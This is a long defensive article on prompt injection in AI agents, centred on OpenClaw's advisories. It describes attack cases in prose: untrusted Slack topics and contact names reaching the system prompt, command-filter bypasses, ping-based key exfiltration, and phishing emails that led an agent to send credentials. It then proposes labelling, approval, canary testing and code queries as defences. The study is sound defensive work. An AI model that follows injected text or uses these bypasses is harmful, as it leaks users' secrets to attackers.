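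The sender-name mistake also recurred in a place that such a function might not have covered. The Hacker News reports that an analyst, using search rules based on earlier advisories, found five more flaws in the code for Slack, Discord, Matrix, Zalo and Microsoft Teams. When OpenClaw started, it looked up the people on the approved list by display name. An attacker who had taken an approved person's name could get onto the list at that point, and later checks would accept the attacker's real ID. Discord and Matrix were already among the apps in the group of 13.

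### The command filter

OpenClaw's command filter decides which shell commands the agent may run without asking. It accounts for 77 of the 470 advisories, up from 46 of the 190. Suwansathit and colleagues trace the problem to one assumption, that the text of a command reveals what it will do. Three bypasses that the developers fixed in late February 2026 show how this can fail:

- The shell can join two lines into one command, but the filter read them differently and missed a command hidden across the break.
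- BusyBox is a single program that contains many small tools, including a shell. Once a user had approved it for one shell command, the agent could use it to run others without approval.
- Some programs accept shortened names for their options. The filter blocked a forbidden option of the `sort` program when the agent wrote its full name, but not when it used a shorter form.

GitLab's summaries include other mismatches of this kind. For example, the filter could approve a command before the shell replaced a wildcard with real file names, and it did not account for how Windows interprets special characters.

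Suwansathit and colleagues suggest running approved programs directly, without a shell. That would prevent the line-joining trick, but not the other two, because BusyBox and `sort` interpret their own arguments. The filter may therefore need several repairs even if all its flaws come from the same assumption. The figure of 77 is a count of advisories about one component, not of variants of one bug, and the researchers examined only the three bypasses above in detail.

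### What the counts measure

The researchers classed only 11 of the 470 advisories (2.3%) under the context window, compared with five of the 190 (2.6%). This probably undercounts flaws that gave outside text too much authority, because they assigned each advisory to one component. A flaw in a webhook or a Slack connection could easily count under the component that received the text.

The paper also describes some flaws differently from the advisories. According to the paper, log headers go straight into the model's context, but GitLab's advisory describes a log that a model might read later. Small differences like this matter because the category has only 11 members.

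The total depends heavily on how many people were looking for flaws, and it grew faster than the danger in OpenClaw's code. OpenClaw gained more than 200,000 GitHub stars, a rough sign of popularity, within weeks of its relaunch in January 2026. A coordinated audit produced the first 73 advisories by 16 February. Researchers filed another 150 in the next twelve days, while the developers were still merging repairs from the audit, and 247 more by mid-April.

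The command filter's share of advisories fell from 24.2% in the February set to 16.4% in the full set, while the share for chat connections rose from 18.4% to 25.3%. These changes may have more to do with where researchers chose to look than with where the most flaws were.

The number of advisories is also only a rough measure of the number of distinct flaws. GitLab's list includes two entries with the same description of a flaw in how OpenClaw accepted configuration changes, and Corgea still lists the withdrawn duplicate of the scheduled-job advisory. But some reported problems may never become advisories, because OpenClaw's security documentation lists findings that the project closes without action under its trust model.

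In *Then there's prompt injection, a malicious email,* Akhond, Khatun and Uddin (2026) read 358 issues labelled as security-related in OpenClaw's GitHub repository and kept the 180 that described a concrete concern. They added 162 Reddit posts and concluded that the problems reflect recurring failures at trust boundaries rather than isolated bugs. Their conclusion supports the pattern in the advisories, but they did not confirm that attackers could exploit each problem, and they sorted the reports by type of weakness rather than root cause.

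Researchers have studied OpenClaw heavily, which makes it useful for learning how flaws recur but not for comparing products. An agent with few advisories might be safer, or it might have the same open paths and fewer people looking for them. The dated repairs are more useful here than the advisory totals, because the wake webhook was open before the Slack repair regardless of how many researchers were studying the code.

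### Other agents

OpenClaw still seems to be the only agent with a dated public series of this kind. Imperva saw other personal assistants insert contacts and similar objects into prompts in a similar way, but does not name them or say how many it examined. This suggests that other developers make the same mistake, but it does not show how often fixing a flaw in another agent leaves a similar one in place.

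The broadest comparison across products is IDEsaster, a collection of more than 30 flaws in AI coding tools that the security researcher Ari Marzouk published in December 2025. Twenty-four of the flaws have CVE numbers, and every product tested was vulnerable. IDEsaster covers a different problem, which is how attackers can use ordinary features of the code editor to do damage after a prompt injection has succeeded. In one attack, the hijacked agent writes a file that refers to a web address, and the editor automatically fetches that address, sending stolen data to the attacker.

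IDEsaster therefore shows that many products share a weakness in what a hijacked agent can do. This is separate from how text gains authority on its way to the model, so a code editor could label every piece of outside text correctly and still be open to these attacks.

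## Which class of bug can be removed

Whether developers can remove a whole vulnerability class depends on the rule that defines it. For untrusted text in an agent, there are three candidates:

- **The exclusion rule:** no untrusted text enters the model context.
- **The labelling rule:** no untrusted text enters a trusted channel or reaches the model without a mark showing that it came from outside.
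- **The approval rule:** no untrusted text influences a consequential action, such as a payment or an outgoing email, unless the user approves it.

### Keeping outside text away from the model

The exclusion rule is the easiest to check in code, because every path from an untrusted source to the prompt builder violates it. An agent that followed it would be safe from indirect injection, but it could not read a web page or summarise an email. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes a user asking a browser agent to summarise unread mail. One message might tell the agent to forward tax documents to a stranger, and the agent has to read that message to summarise the mail.

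The rule suits narrow programs, such as MITRE's chatbot that needs only two catalogue numbers, but it can also apply to parts of a larger agent. OpenClaw's *Prompt injection* suggests having a separate reader agent, with its tools disabled, summarise untrusted content for the main agent. A hijacked reader can then do little damage directly. But whoever wrote the content can influence the summary, so the main agent still receives untrusted text. To keep that text out completely, the reader would have to return something much more limited, such as a date or a yes or no.

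### Labelling outside text

The labelling rule lets the agent read the email and restricts only how its text is passed to the model. It forbids copying a Slack topic into the system prompt, or pasting a contact's name into the user's message without marking its source. Code can check this because a text's origin and assigned role are facts about the program and don't depend on how a model will react.

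The standard definition of the prompt injection weakness depends on the model. In MITRE's catalogue, a program has the weakness if the way it builds prompts causes the model to confuse user input with the developer's instructions. The same code could therefore have the weakness with one model but not another. MITRE adds that indirect injection may have a different root cause, such as a program using a source it should not have trusted.

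One of MITRE's example repairs is also hard to check in code. A user gets a joke-telling agent to reveal a secret token in its system prompt, and the repair adds an instruction not to reveal the token. Only repeated testing can show how often the model obeys. MITRE then suggests keeping secrets out of the prompt.

A label is useful only if outside text can't imitate it. OpenClaw puts boundary markers around outside content and removes any chat-template markers inside it. Otherwise, some servers for open models would treat a typed marker as a real one, and a web page could start a fake system message. OpenClaw removes these markers in the same step that adds the label, so text that skips this step keeps its chat-template markers. Operators can switch off labelling for webhooks, Gmail messages and scheduled jobs, although OpenClaw advises against this in normal use. A developer checking the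 rule would have to treat each of these settings as an exception.

The labelling rule interferes with some useful features that are meant to take instructions from outside text, such as the AGENTS.md file in a downloaded project, add-on skills, and tool descriptions from someone else's server. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), by researchers from Google, NVIDIA and several universities, compares these with the scripts that a web page loads. A browser can usually identify the address a script came from and restrict what it does, but an agent has much less reliable information about the source of an instruction. Developers can keep such features by requiring an endorsement, which is an explicit, reviewable step that raises the trust label of a particular piece of text.

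Scaffolding developers also have to decide which stores of text to trust. OpenClaw's *Security Policy* treats the agent's memory files as trusted, on the grounds that anyone who can edit them already has the operator's access. That reasoning doesn't cover text the agent copied into memory from a web page.

### Requiring approval for actions

The approval rule limits the damage even when the model fully follows an attacker's instructions. A stranger's email could not trigger a payment by itself, even if the program had mislabelled it.

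A model processes its whole context together, so the program can't tell which sentence led to a tool request. It can instead enforce a stricter rule by requiring approval for every consequential action once the agent has read any untrusted text. David C passes on a similar idea from Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, that a model's privileges should drop to those of the person whose text it is processing. An agent reading a stranger's email would then have no more privileges than the stranger.

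Such an agent could still summarise the inbox, but it could not answer routine mail overnight. Its user might also have to approve so many requests that they stop reading them. Some experimental systems try to reduce both problems by tracking how far each part of the model's output can be trusted.

Developers must also decide which actions are consequential, and they can easily miss one. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, asked for approval before running many commands that could send data to unknown places, but not before running `ping`, which checks whether another computer responds. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes how a prompt hidden in a code file could make the agent read secret keys and include them in the name of the computer to contact. When `ping` looked up that name, it sent the keys to the attacker.

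### The SQL injection objection

David C argues that comparing prompt injection with SQL injection is dangerous because it encourages developers to expect a similar fix. Parameterised queries prevent SQL injection because a database handles commands and data differently, whereas a language model only predicts the next token from the text so far. Developers can mark the data, train the model to give it less weight or try to detect attacks, but these methods all add a distinction that the model does not inherently make.

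David C describes a language model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a privileged program that someone with fewer privileges tricks into misusing its access. Developers can normally fix this kind of flaw. With a language model, he says, they can only make attacks less likely or less harmful, and a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk may not be a good place to use one.

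*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* goes further and conjectures that persistent attackers will always get past defences that rely on the model to separate instructions from data. The conjecture is based on experience with image classifiers and, later, language models, and nobody has proved it.

OpenAI took a similar position in December 2025, saying that prompt injection was unlikely ever to be fully "solved" and comparing it to online scams. The company had trained a model to attack its browser agent, and the model could test each attack in a simulator and improve it. In one of these attacks, the user asked for an out-of-office reply, but an email already in the inbox got the agent to send the user's resignation to the chief executive instead. OpenAI used attacks like this to train a more resistant version of the agent.

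Models have become much harder to hijack since then. In August 2026, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, about 0.05% of direct attacks and 3.77% of indirect attacks succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol in OpenAI's tests. In October, GPT-6 Sol resisted 99.99% of direct attacks and 97.13% of indirect attacks, according to Cross (2026) in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*. The Decoder reports that in Anthropic's results for Opus 5, no attacks succeeded in 129 browser scenarios. On a more general test by the security company Gray Swan, attackers succeeded against Opus 5 in 2.0% of cases after 15 attempts, down from 5.5% for Opus 4.8.

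These figures come from different tests, so they can't rank the two companies' models. They also offer no guarantee like that of a parameterised query, which holds however many times an attacker tries. If each indirect attack on GPT-6 Sol had an independent 2.87% chance of success, an attacker who sent 24 emails would have about an even chance of succeeding at least once. Real attempts are not independent, and some attacks work far better than others, but an attacker can often keep trying for very little money.

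Training agents on more attacks may not eliminate prompt injection either. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection thousands*, reports research in which such training left agents easier to hijack, and warns that a large collection of attacks may repeat the same one many times. In June 2026, Ariel Fogel of OWASP, which publishes software security guidance, still called prompt injection an "unresolved problem" (Poireault, 2026, *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns*).

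### What the labelling rule can guarantee

With a parameterised query, the program keeps the visitor's text separate from the query, and the database never executes it. Agent developers can also keep untrusted text separate, but they can't guarantee that the model will never follow instructions in it. The labelling rule requires only the separation, which ordinary code can do, so the objection does not apply to it.

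Accurate labels are worth having because even a model that respected every role would obey a stranger's words if they appeared in a system message. The approval rule also depends on accurate labels, because the program that enforces it limits an agent's actions according to who wrote the text.

It is less clear how much a correct label changes the model's behaviour. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell found that the style of a text tends to override its label, which suggests that the effect may be limited. The contact attack on OpenClaw worked when the text had no label, but Imperva does not report repeating it after the repair, so the result doesn't show how much the new label helps.

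David C agrees that marking data can make injection harder, but he puts more weight on ordinary code that limits what the system can do. He also warns customers about any product that claims to "stop" prompt injection. Removing every labelling bug would ensure that outside text never arrives disguised as an instruction from the developer, but it would not fix prompt injection.

### The Varonis email test

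*Phishing for Lobsters* (2026), by the security company Varonis, shows how much can go wrong without such a disguise. Researchers connected an OpenClaw agent called Pinchy to a Gmail inbox filled with invented business mail and fake secrets. They tested it with Gemini 3.1 Pro and GPT-5.4, and with two sets of standing instructions. The stricter set told the agent to verify people's identities before acting on sensitive requests.

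In the first test, someone claiming to be a team leader named Dan wrote from an outside Gmail account. He said there was a production problem and asked for access to the staging environment, where developers try out software before release. Pinchy searched the mailbox and sent him cloud access keys, database passwords and login details for a server. In the second test, the sender asked for the week's customer export, saying he was working from home on a presentation. Pinchy sent records of 247 fictional companies, including contract dates and about $1.28 million in monthly revenue. Pinchy failed both tests under both sets of instructions.

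Neither email needed to pose as a system message or hide a command in another document. Varonis does not report how OpenClaw labelled the emails, but an accurate label would have added only that the request came from an outside email, which the sender's address already showed. Varonis calls this "agent phishing" to distinguish it from indirect prompt injection, but concedes that some of its tests fall between the two. The distinction makes little difference to the three rules. The exclusion rule would have prevented both attacks by keeping the agent from reading mail. The labelling rule would have allowed them, and the approval rule would have held the replies until the user had seen them.

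The agent was better at spotting technical tricks. When asked to grant access to a malicious application disguised as a timesheet service, it investigated the address behind the request and stopped. Under the looser instructions, it opened a fake gift card page, but it filled in the form with made-up details and eventually recognised the page as phishing.

Adding a section on email safety to the agent's instructions reduced successful attacks but did not fully prevent the theft of credentials. Varonis also recommends controls outside the model, such as requiring human approval before the agent writes to a new address and limiting its access to company data when an outside email starts the task. The Hacker News points out that OpenClaw could patch the contact flaw, but that no patch fixes the weakness Varonis found.

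Four scenarios can show that such an attack is possible, but not how often it would succeed. In another public test, described by Willison (2026), Fernando Irarrázaval invited people to email an OpenClaw agent and extract its secrets. About 2,000 people made 6,000 attempts, but nobody succeeded. That agent ran on Opus 4.6, and its instructions explicitly forbade it to reveal credentials in response to anything in an email. The two tests used different models, instructions and tasks, so comparing them doesn't show which difference mattered most.

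### What OpenClaw counts as a vulnerability

The Varonis result would probably not count as a vulnerability under OpenClaw's security policy, because the agent had permission to read the mailbox and send mail. OpenClaw tells operators to assume that injected text can manipulate the model. It accepts a report of prompt injection only if the attack also crosses one of five security boundaries: trust in the host machine and its configuration, authentication, tool policy, sandboxing, and approvals for running commands. A copy of what seems to be an earlier version of the policy excluded prompt injection attacks without this exception.

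One OpenClaw advisory describes a bug that does count, because the injection crossed a boundary and the developers had a specific mistake in the code to repair. OpenClaw kept a list of settings that the model could not change, but the developers had to update it by hand, and it fell behind as they added settings. According to OSV, a hijacked model with access to the owner's configuration tool could change settings that affected how commands ran, and the changes could survive a restart.

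The policy fits David C's advice to enforce security outside the model, and it means the developers don't have to handle every clever email as a separate bug. But it makes the result depend on which boundaries are switched on. According to OpenClaw's *Security trust model*, the agent can run commands on the user's machine without asking by default, and sandboxing is off by default. An attack that gets the agent to run a stranger's program may therefore cross no listed boundary on a standard installation.

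Labelling is not on the list of boundaries, and OpenClaw seems to have handled labelling bugs inconsistently. The Slack flaw received a CVE number because OpenClaw treated untrusted channel information as "higher-trust system input" (OSV, *OpenClaw has Remote Code Execution via System Prompt Injection in Slack Channel*, 2026). Imperva calls the contact and location flaws vulnerabilities and reports that OpenClaw fixed them, but mentions no CVE number.

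These decisions greatly affect the totals. OpenClaw says it received 1,309 reports through GitHub between 10 January and 30 April 2026. It published 535 of them and closed 746 as invalid. Of the 109 reports marked critical, it published only 14. OpenClaw's founder says many of the rejected reports described intended features, such as the agent's ability to run commands, as flaws. He does not say how many concerned prompt injection, so the number of labelling bugs among the 746 is unknown.

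A fall in OpenClaw's advisories would therefore not show that its agents had become harder to persuade. A project that published every successful injection would have more advisories for the same code. Developers who want to remove the labelling class need to check past code changes as well as advisories, because a search of OpenClaw's advisories would find the Slack topics but could easily miss the contact names.

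## Listing every path into the model's context

Developers can check how an agent labels a piece of text only if they know that the text reaches the model. An agent may collect text in dozens of places, but it calls the model from only a few, so it is easier to start at the model and work backwards:

1. Find every call to a model provider.
2. For each call, find every function that contributes text to it.
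3. Trace each piece of text back to whoever can write it.

### From the model call to the author

The main loop is rarely the only code that calls a model. An agent may also call one to summarise a long conversation or to run a sub-agent, a helper with its own context. Searching the code for the provider's software library can miss calls sent as ordinary web requests. *Comment and Control* (Fendley, Liu and colleagues, 2026) describes a tool that records model requests in automated GitHub workflows and can monitor calls made either through the library or as ordinary web requests.

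OpenClaw's *Context* offers a useful starting list for finding the functions that contribute text. The model receives the system prompt, the conversation history, tool calls and their results, attachments, summaries of older messages, and hidden text added by the provider. The system prompt contains lists of tools and skills, the workspace location, the time and up to seven workspace files. According to OpenClaw, it also has a section on the current group chat and a line that can include the code repository's location. Plugins can replace the code that assembles all this, so an inventory of one installation may not fit another.

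Much of this text enters the context before the user asks for anything. Anthropic's *context window* lists what Claude Code loads at the start: an instruction file, notes from its automatic memory, the names of MCP tools and the descriptions of skills.

Tracing can stop at text that is fixed in the source code, or at a person or program outside the agent. It should not stop at a file or a database, because somebody wrote the contents. The path can also run outside the agent's own code. In one workflow that Fendley and colleagues studied, a comment on GitHub passed through the project's workflow file and a reusable component from another repository before it reached Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent. Gemini CLI's code alone would not show that a stranger had written part of the prompt.

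Automated code search can help with the tracing, but it often fails to find where the data came from. Cui (2026), in *Beyond Predefined Sinks*, traced data backwards from 23,866 sensitive operations, such as running a command, in 67 agent projects and found a possible source for 41% of the operations. The rest may have no outside source, or the analysis may have missed it.

In *What's in Your Agent's Context?*, Li, Cui and colleagues (2026) listed the sources of text in the context of 12 agents, including Codex, Claude Code and OpenClaw. They had an AI model read each agent's source code, find the main loop and the format of its model requests, and list every source of text with its role. The model listed 463 sources, and tests on the running agents confirmed 282 of them. OpenClaw had the most confirmed sources (41) and Claude Code the fewest (15).

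The researchers also spent 40 hours making inventories of Codex and Gemini CLI by hand. The model had found 28 of the 30 sources on their list for Codex and 38 of the 42 for Gemini CLI. An AI model can therefore produce a good first draft, but developers still need to look for the sources it missed.

### Who can write each source

| Source | Who can write it | How it can reach the model |
|---|---|---|
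| Messages and their metadata | the sender, or anyone who can edit a name, topic or subject line | chat text, channel topics, contact names |
| Retrieved pages | the site's owner and anyone who can post there | page text, titles, addresses |
| Tool results and errors | whoever runs the tool or supplies its data | command output, or an error that quotes its input |
| Tool descriptions | whoever runs the tool's server | the tool list, before any tool runs |
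| Repository instruction files | anyone who contributes to the project | AGENTS.md and similar files |
| File names, directory names and commit messages | contributors, or whoever packed a downloaded archive | folder listings and recent project history |
| Logs | anyone whose request the program logs | the agent reads the log to investigate a problem |
| Memory | the user, and the agent, which may copy text from anywhere | notes from earlier sessions |
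| Skills | the skill's author, or anyone who can get a file into a skill folder | descriptions at the start, full instructions on use |
| Other agents' output | the other agent, and whoever wrote what it read | reports and messages |
| History summaries | a model, working from everything in the conversation | a substitute for older messages |
| Text in images | whoever made the image or wrote something that appears in it | screenshots, scans and photographs |
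| Settings files | the user, project contributors and often the agent itself | extra instructions, or a list of folders to load |

Often, more people can write to a source than it seems. In the version that Li and colleagues tested, Claude Code put the project's five most recent commit messages, which are contributors' short notes about their code changes, into its system prompt. When a maintainer opens a stranger's proposed change for review, the stranger's commit messages can be among those five, even if the maintainer later rejects the change. Gemini CLI searched every subfolder for instruction files, so one deep in a project could reach the model too.

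Settings files were the largest group, with 97 of the 282 confirmed sources. Most developers would probably think of web pages and emails first.

The same kind of text can also have different roles in different agents. Codex and Claude Code load a project's instruction file as a user message, while OpenClaw and Cline put it in the system prompt, so developers can't copy the roles from another product's inventory. Across all 12 agents, 183 of the 282 sources entered under the system role and only 30 under the tool role.

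Some of those 183 are settings or instructions in the user's home folder, which a stranger normally can't edit, so not all of them are labelling bugs. The researchers still describe all 282 sources as vulnerable, because an attacker might get the agent to edit such files.

### Delayed paths

On a delayed path, the agent stores text in one session and reads it in another. Two functions from an imaginary agent show why such paths are easy to miss:

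```
def finish_browsing(page):
    memory.save(first_line(page))

def start_session():
    context.add(role="system", text=memory.load())
```

`finish_browsing` saves a page title to the agent's notes without calling the model, and `start_session` loads those notes into the system prompt. Each function looks reasonable to a reviewer who checks it alone, but together they put text from a stranger's web page into the system prompt.

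To find these paths, developers can treat every store of text as both a sink and a source. They list every function that writes to the store or reads from it, and give any text read from it the trust level of the store's least trusted writer. Besides memory, the stores include logs, saved conversations, scheduled jobs, skill folders and settings files.

Some delayed paths have no function that copies the text. Most agents have a general tool for writing files, and text on a web page might lead the model to add a sentence to AGENTS.md with that tool. In the next session, the scaffolding would load that sentence as a standing instruction.

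Li and colleagues tested this possibility on 1,761 pairs of sources. In each pair, one source had a higher role than the other or lasted longer. In the less privileged source, they planted an instruction to copy text into the more privileged one. They then deleted the original and restarted the agent with an unrelated task. With GPT-5.5, the copied text reached the model in 1,315 pairs, or about three-quarters.

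An inventory should record whether the agent can write to each file the scaffolding loads. Ten of the 12 agents could change their own settings files when the user had turned off approval requests. The other two, Claude Code and Aider, still asked for permission.

Stored text may re-enter the model's context within the same session. Several agents, including Codex and OpenClaw, watch their skill folders and load any new or changed skill immediately. When Claude Code opens a file, it also loads any instruction file in the same folder, so a downloaded archive can add instructions in the middle of a task.

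Summaries cause a similar problem. When a conversation grows long, OpenClaw saves a summary of the older messages. That summary may include a claim from a web page, reworded and without its label. Tracking influence through a paraphrase requires different methods.

### Three questions at each trust boundary

Zhang and colleagues developed a way to decide which code around these paths to inspect, and used it to plan ClawAudit, the tool with which they audited OpenClaw's source code. They first diagrammed how data moves through OpenClaw and marked three trust boundaries, where the program takes in something it does not control and turns it into something privileged. The boundaries were where user input enters the agent, where the agent hands work to tools and skills, and where it contacts outside services.

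At each boundary, the researchers asked:

- What attacker-controlled data crosses it?
- What privileged operation follows?
- Which component stands between them?

For the Slack flaw, the data is the channel topic, the privileged operation is adding text to the system prompt, and the component is the prompt builder. For the wake webhook, the data might be the subject line of a stranger's email, the privileged operation is creating a trusted system event, and the component is the webhook handler.

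Naming the component lets a developer know which code to read, though there may be more than one component. For example, each of OpenClaw's chat connections checks senders separately, so a developer has to read the code for all 15 that Suwansathit and colleagues count.

Zhang and colleagues used STRIDE, a standard checklist of six kinds of threat, to turn the answers into categories of flaw. They split one of the six, tampering, into untrusted text entering a prompt and untrusted data controlling what a tool does. A rule written to find one of these flaws would miss the other. The prompt category includes the memory writer. This helps with delayed paths because the program may still have a record of where a piece of text came from when it saves it.

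The scheme sorts flaws by where developers would fix them, so it puts untrusted headers in a log under network and communication rather than under prompts. That makes sense for assigning the fix, but an inventory organised the same way could leave out the path from the log to the model.

### Testing the list with unique strings

Developers can check the inventory by running the agent. They put a different harmless string, known as a canary, in each source, give the agent ordinary tasks and record every request it sends to the model. They then search the requests for the canaries and note where each one appears, under which role and with what label.

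Each request should be recorded as it leaves the program, because code that runs earlier may not have the final text. Some products already make this easy. VS Code's *Debug chat interactions* describes a view in Microsoft's code editor that shows the prompt, context and tools sent to the model. OpenClaw's `/context` command would not be enough, because it reports the size of each part but not the full text. Even a complete recording of the request omits anything the provider adds on its own servers, such as OpenAI's system message.

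Fendley and colleagues put the name of the event and the field into each canary string, so a match shows where the text came from. They also record how the workflow cut or reformatted the text, and which headings and warnings surround it in the final request. *Can Agents Trust Their Skills?* (2026) used canaries to check 1,566 possible paths from add-on skills to sensitive operations in 11 agents. Each canary depends only on which test it belongs to, so repeating a test produces the same string.

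Li and colleagues used random strings and hid them from the AI model that prepared the tests, so the model could not fake a match. They started each agent twice in one project folder and once in another. A string that appeared all three times came from a source that affects every project. A string that appeared both times in the first folder but not in the second came from a source tied to the first project.

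Suppose the developer of an office agent lists 12 sources and plants a string in each, `heron-01` to `heron-12`. The developer then asks the agent to read an email, look up a web page, check a calendar and review a code change.

| String | Source | Where it appears |
|---|---|---|
| `heron-01` | body of an email | tool result |
| `heron-02` | subject line of the email | **system event** |
| `heron-03` | text of a web page | tool result |
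| `heron-04` | title of the web page | tool result |
| `heron-05` | calendar entry | tool result |
| `heron-06` | project README | tool result |
| `heron-07` | name of a file in the project | **system prompt** |
| `heron-08` | commit message | tool result |
| `heron-09` | report from another agent | tool result |
| `heron-10` | note that the agent saves to memory | not found |
| `heron-11` | error message from the mail server | not found |
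| `heron-12` | text in an attached image | not found |

Nine strings appear, seven of them in tool results, where outside text belongs. The other two, the email's subject line and the file name, are in trusted channels. A stranger can choose either one, so both break the labelling rule and are bugs for the developer to fix.

The search should continue after the first match, because the file name could appear correctly in one tool result and again in the system prompt. A developer who stopped at the tool result would miss the bug.

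### When a string does not appear

The three paths may still exist even though their strings are missing. The agent saved the memory note, but it loads its memory only at the start of a session. The mail server worked normally, so it never produced an error. The image reached the model as image data, which the model may be able to read but a text search can't.

When the developer starts a second session, `heron-10` appears in the system prompt, which reveals a third labelling bug. When they make the mail server reject a message, `heron-11` appears in a tool result. They can also check whether the request contains the image and, if so, under which role.

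Strings can go missing for other reasons too. By default, OpenClaw includes at most 20,000 characters of each workspace file, so a string near the end of a long file could fail to reach the model even though text near the top does. A program might change the string's format, or a model might leave it out of a summary. The path might also depend on a plugin that the developer has not installed.

Li and colleagues could not set up a working test for 20 sources. They also excluded 161 sources from testing, mainly on the grounds that an attacker could not put arbitrary text in them, but a manual review found that five had been wrongly excluded. One was the language setting in Aider, a coding agent. An AI model had judged the setting too restricted to hold an instruction, but Aider hardly checked the setting's contents.

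A match does not always mean that an attacker could use the path, because some folder names and settings can hold a short test string but not a full sentence.

Developers should therefore record why each missing string did not appear in the model's context. They can safely close a path if the code blocks outside text, as with the MITRE chatbot that accepts only catalogue numbers. Otherwise, they should keep the path on the list as untested.

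This kind of test also misses any source in which nobody planted a string. The recorded requests can help find such sources, because every piece of text in a request should come from either the program's source code or a source on the list. If the developer can't trace some text to either, the list is probably missing a source.

### Recording where text came from

A test with unique strings covers one version of an agent on a few tasks. Other tools record where text came from (its provenance) while people use the agent.

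OpenTelemetry, an open standard for recording what software does, is the most general option. Its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans*, still in development, defines a format for model requests. The format can hold the system instructions, the tool definitions, and each message in order with its role. Developers have to turn this recording on, since messages may contain private information, and a program may shorten what it records. The format has no standard field for where the text inside a message came from, so a web page's title inside a system message would look the same as the developer's own words.

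*LMLineage* (2026) records each sentence's type of source (such as web content or memory), its web address or file, and a confidence score. These details stay with the text when later turns reuse it. The program can identify with certainty which page an input sentence came from, but it can only estimate which inputs led the model to write an output sentence. The labelling rule needs only the origin of the input, at least until the agent feeds the model's output back into a prompt.

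A prototype in *Toward Trustworthy Agentic AI* (2025) keeps similar records for parts of images as well as text. It stores a short fingerprint of the content instead of the content itself, to avoid keeping private information.

For delayed paths, *MemLineage* (2026) attaches a record to everything an agent saves in memory. The record identifies who wrote the entry (the user, an agent, a tool or an outsider), its trust level and any earlier entries it came from. A digital signature shows whether someone has changed the record since. But if the program saves a web page's text as the user's own words, the signature will still be valid and won't expose the mistake.

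Researchers have not yet tested such records thoroughly. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 71 works on tracing what agents do. Few reported protecting their records against tampering, and none of the benchmarks in the review tested the whole chain of provenance. The review was selective, so it may have missed relevant work.

*Ghost in the Agent* (2026) has 400 test scenarios built on 20 agent frameworks, and some involve text that one session or agent passes to another. Outside text reaches or influences a sensitive tool call in half of the 400, and does not in the rest. The benchmark's sinks are tool calls, so a tool tested on it could score well and still miss a web page's title entering the system prompt.

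Users of most agents can't see an inventory of context sources. Li and colleagues propose that vendors publish a context manifest, modelled on the component lists some software companies already provide. The manifest would name every source an agent can load, when the agent loads it, which role the source gets and whether it affects one session, one project or all of them. Anyone could then compare the manifests of two releases to see whether a source had moved from a tool result into the system prompt.

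## Writing a code query from one fixed bug

Planting strings in an agent reveals only the paths it takes during the test. A code query searches the source code, so it can find paths that no test has triggered, and developers can run it again on every later version. After OpenClaw's developers took Slack topics out of the system prompt, they could have written a query based on that fix to look for similar bugs. The hard part is deciding how broad to make the query. A query for Slack topics alone would find nothing new, but a very broad one could return so many false alarms that developers miss the real bugs.

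### How CodeQL searches a program

CodeQL is GitHub's code analysis tool. As Trent (2026), in *Must Learn CodeQL*, explains, it first builds a database of the program's structure, the order in which its statements can run, the types of its values and the way data moves between them. A developer then searches the database in a language called QL. Kosman (2025), in *Vulnhalla*, gives a very short query that finds every empty block of code in a C program:

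```
import cpp
from BlockStmt blk
where blk.getNumStmt() = 0
select blk
```

The first line loads CodeQL's library for C and C++. The second takes every code block, the third keeps those with no statements, and the last reports them.

A taint query looks for paths through the program instead of single places. GitHub's *Module CodeInjectionConfig*, the reference page for one such query, describes several settings, including the source, the sink, additional flow steps and barriers. An additional flow step adds a connection that CodeQL would otherwise miss, where data moves from one place to another. A barrier is a place where CodeQL stops following the data, usually because a check has made it safe.

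CodeQL follows data through assignments, joined strings and most function calls. The query may need an extra step where data passes through code outside the database, such as a template library that inserts a folder name into a prompt. Without that step, CodeQL's path stops at the library and the query misses the bug. A badly chosen barrier can also make the query miss bugs, because CodeQL removes the barrier from its data flow graph, along with every path that runs through it.

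### From the Slack topic to the folder name

The function below belongs to an imaginary agent. Each call to `add` puts a message into the model's context, with the role first and the text second.

```
 1  def build_prompt(event):
 2      topic = event.slack.topic
 3      add("system", "Topic: " + topic)
 4      add("system", "Description: " + event.slack.description)
 5      add("system", "Channel ID: " + event.slack.channel_id)
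 6      add("system", "Group: " + event.discord.group_name)
 7      if event.language in ["English", "French"]:
 8          add("system", "Reply in " + event.language)
 9      add("system", "Folder: " + current_folder())
10      add("system", "Scratch folder: " + temp_folder())
11      add("system", "Version: " + read_file("VERSION"))
12      add("system", "Notes: " + read_file("memory.md"))
13      add("user", event.text)
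```

Suppose someone reports that the Slack topic on line 3 reaches the system prompt. A query for that one bug, in pseudocode, would be:

```
find every path
  from     event.slack.topic
  to       the text in add("system", text)
  through  assignments, joined strings and function calls
  unless   a check limits the text to a fixed list
```

The developer first runs the query on the old code, where it should report the path from line 2 to line 3, and then on the repaired code, where it should report nothing. If the query fails either test, it does not describe the bug correctly. A query can pass both tests and still be too narrow to find anything else, as this one is.

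The developer can now widen the source without changing the rest of the query. If every field that Slack supplies counts as a source, the query also flags the channel's description on line 4, which is a real bug. It flags the channel ID on line 5 too, but that is a false alarm because Slack generates the ID and nobody can write an instruction in it.

If the query treats every field of an incoming message from any chat service as a source, it also finds the Discord group name on line 6. The language on line 8 comes from the message too, but line 7 limits it to two values, so the barrier keeps it out of the results.

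Neither version finds the folder name, because the name doesn't come from a message. The developer has to add the names of files and folders as sources. The query then reports line 9, which has the same kind of bug as the one OpenClaw fixed in its working folder. It also raises a false alarm on line 10, where the program chooses the name of its own scratch folder.

Widening the query again to include the contents of files catches line 12, where text from a web page may arrive later through the saved notes. It also adds a false alarm on line 11, which reads a version number that ships with the program.

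| Source in the query | New real bug | New false alarm | Real bugs among all reports |
|---|---|---|---|
| Slack topic | line 3 | none | 1 of 1 |
| any Slack field | line 4 | line 5 | 2 of 3 |
| any field of a message | line 6 | none | 3 of 4 |
| also file and folder names | line 9 | line 10 | 4 of 6 |
| also file contents | line 12 | line 11 | 5 of 8 |

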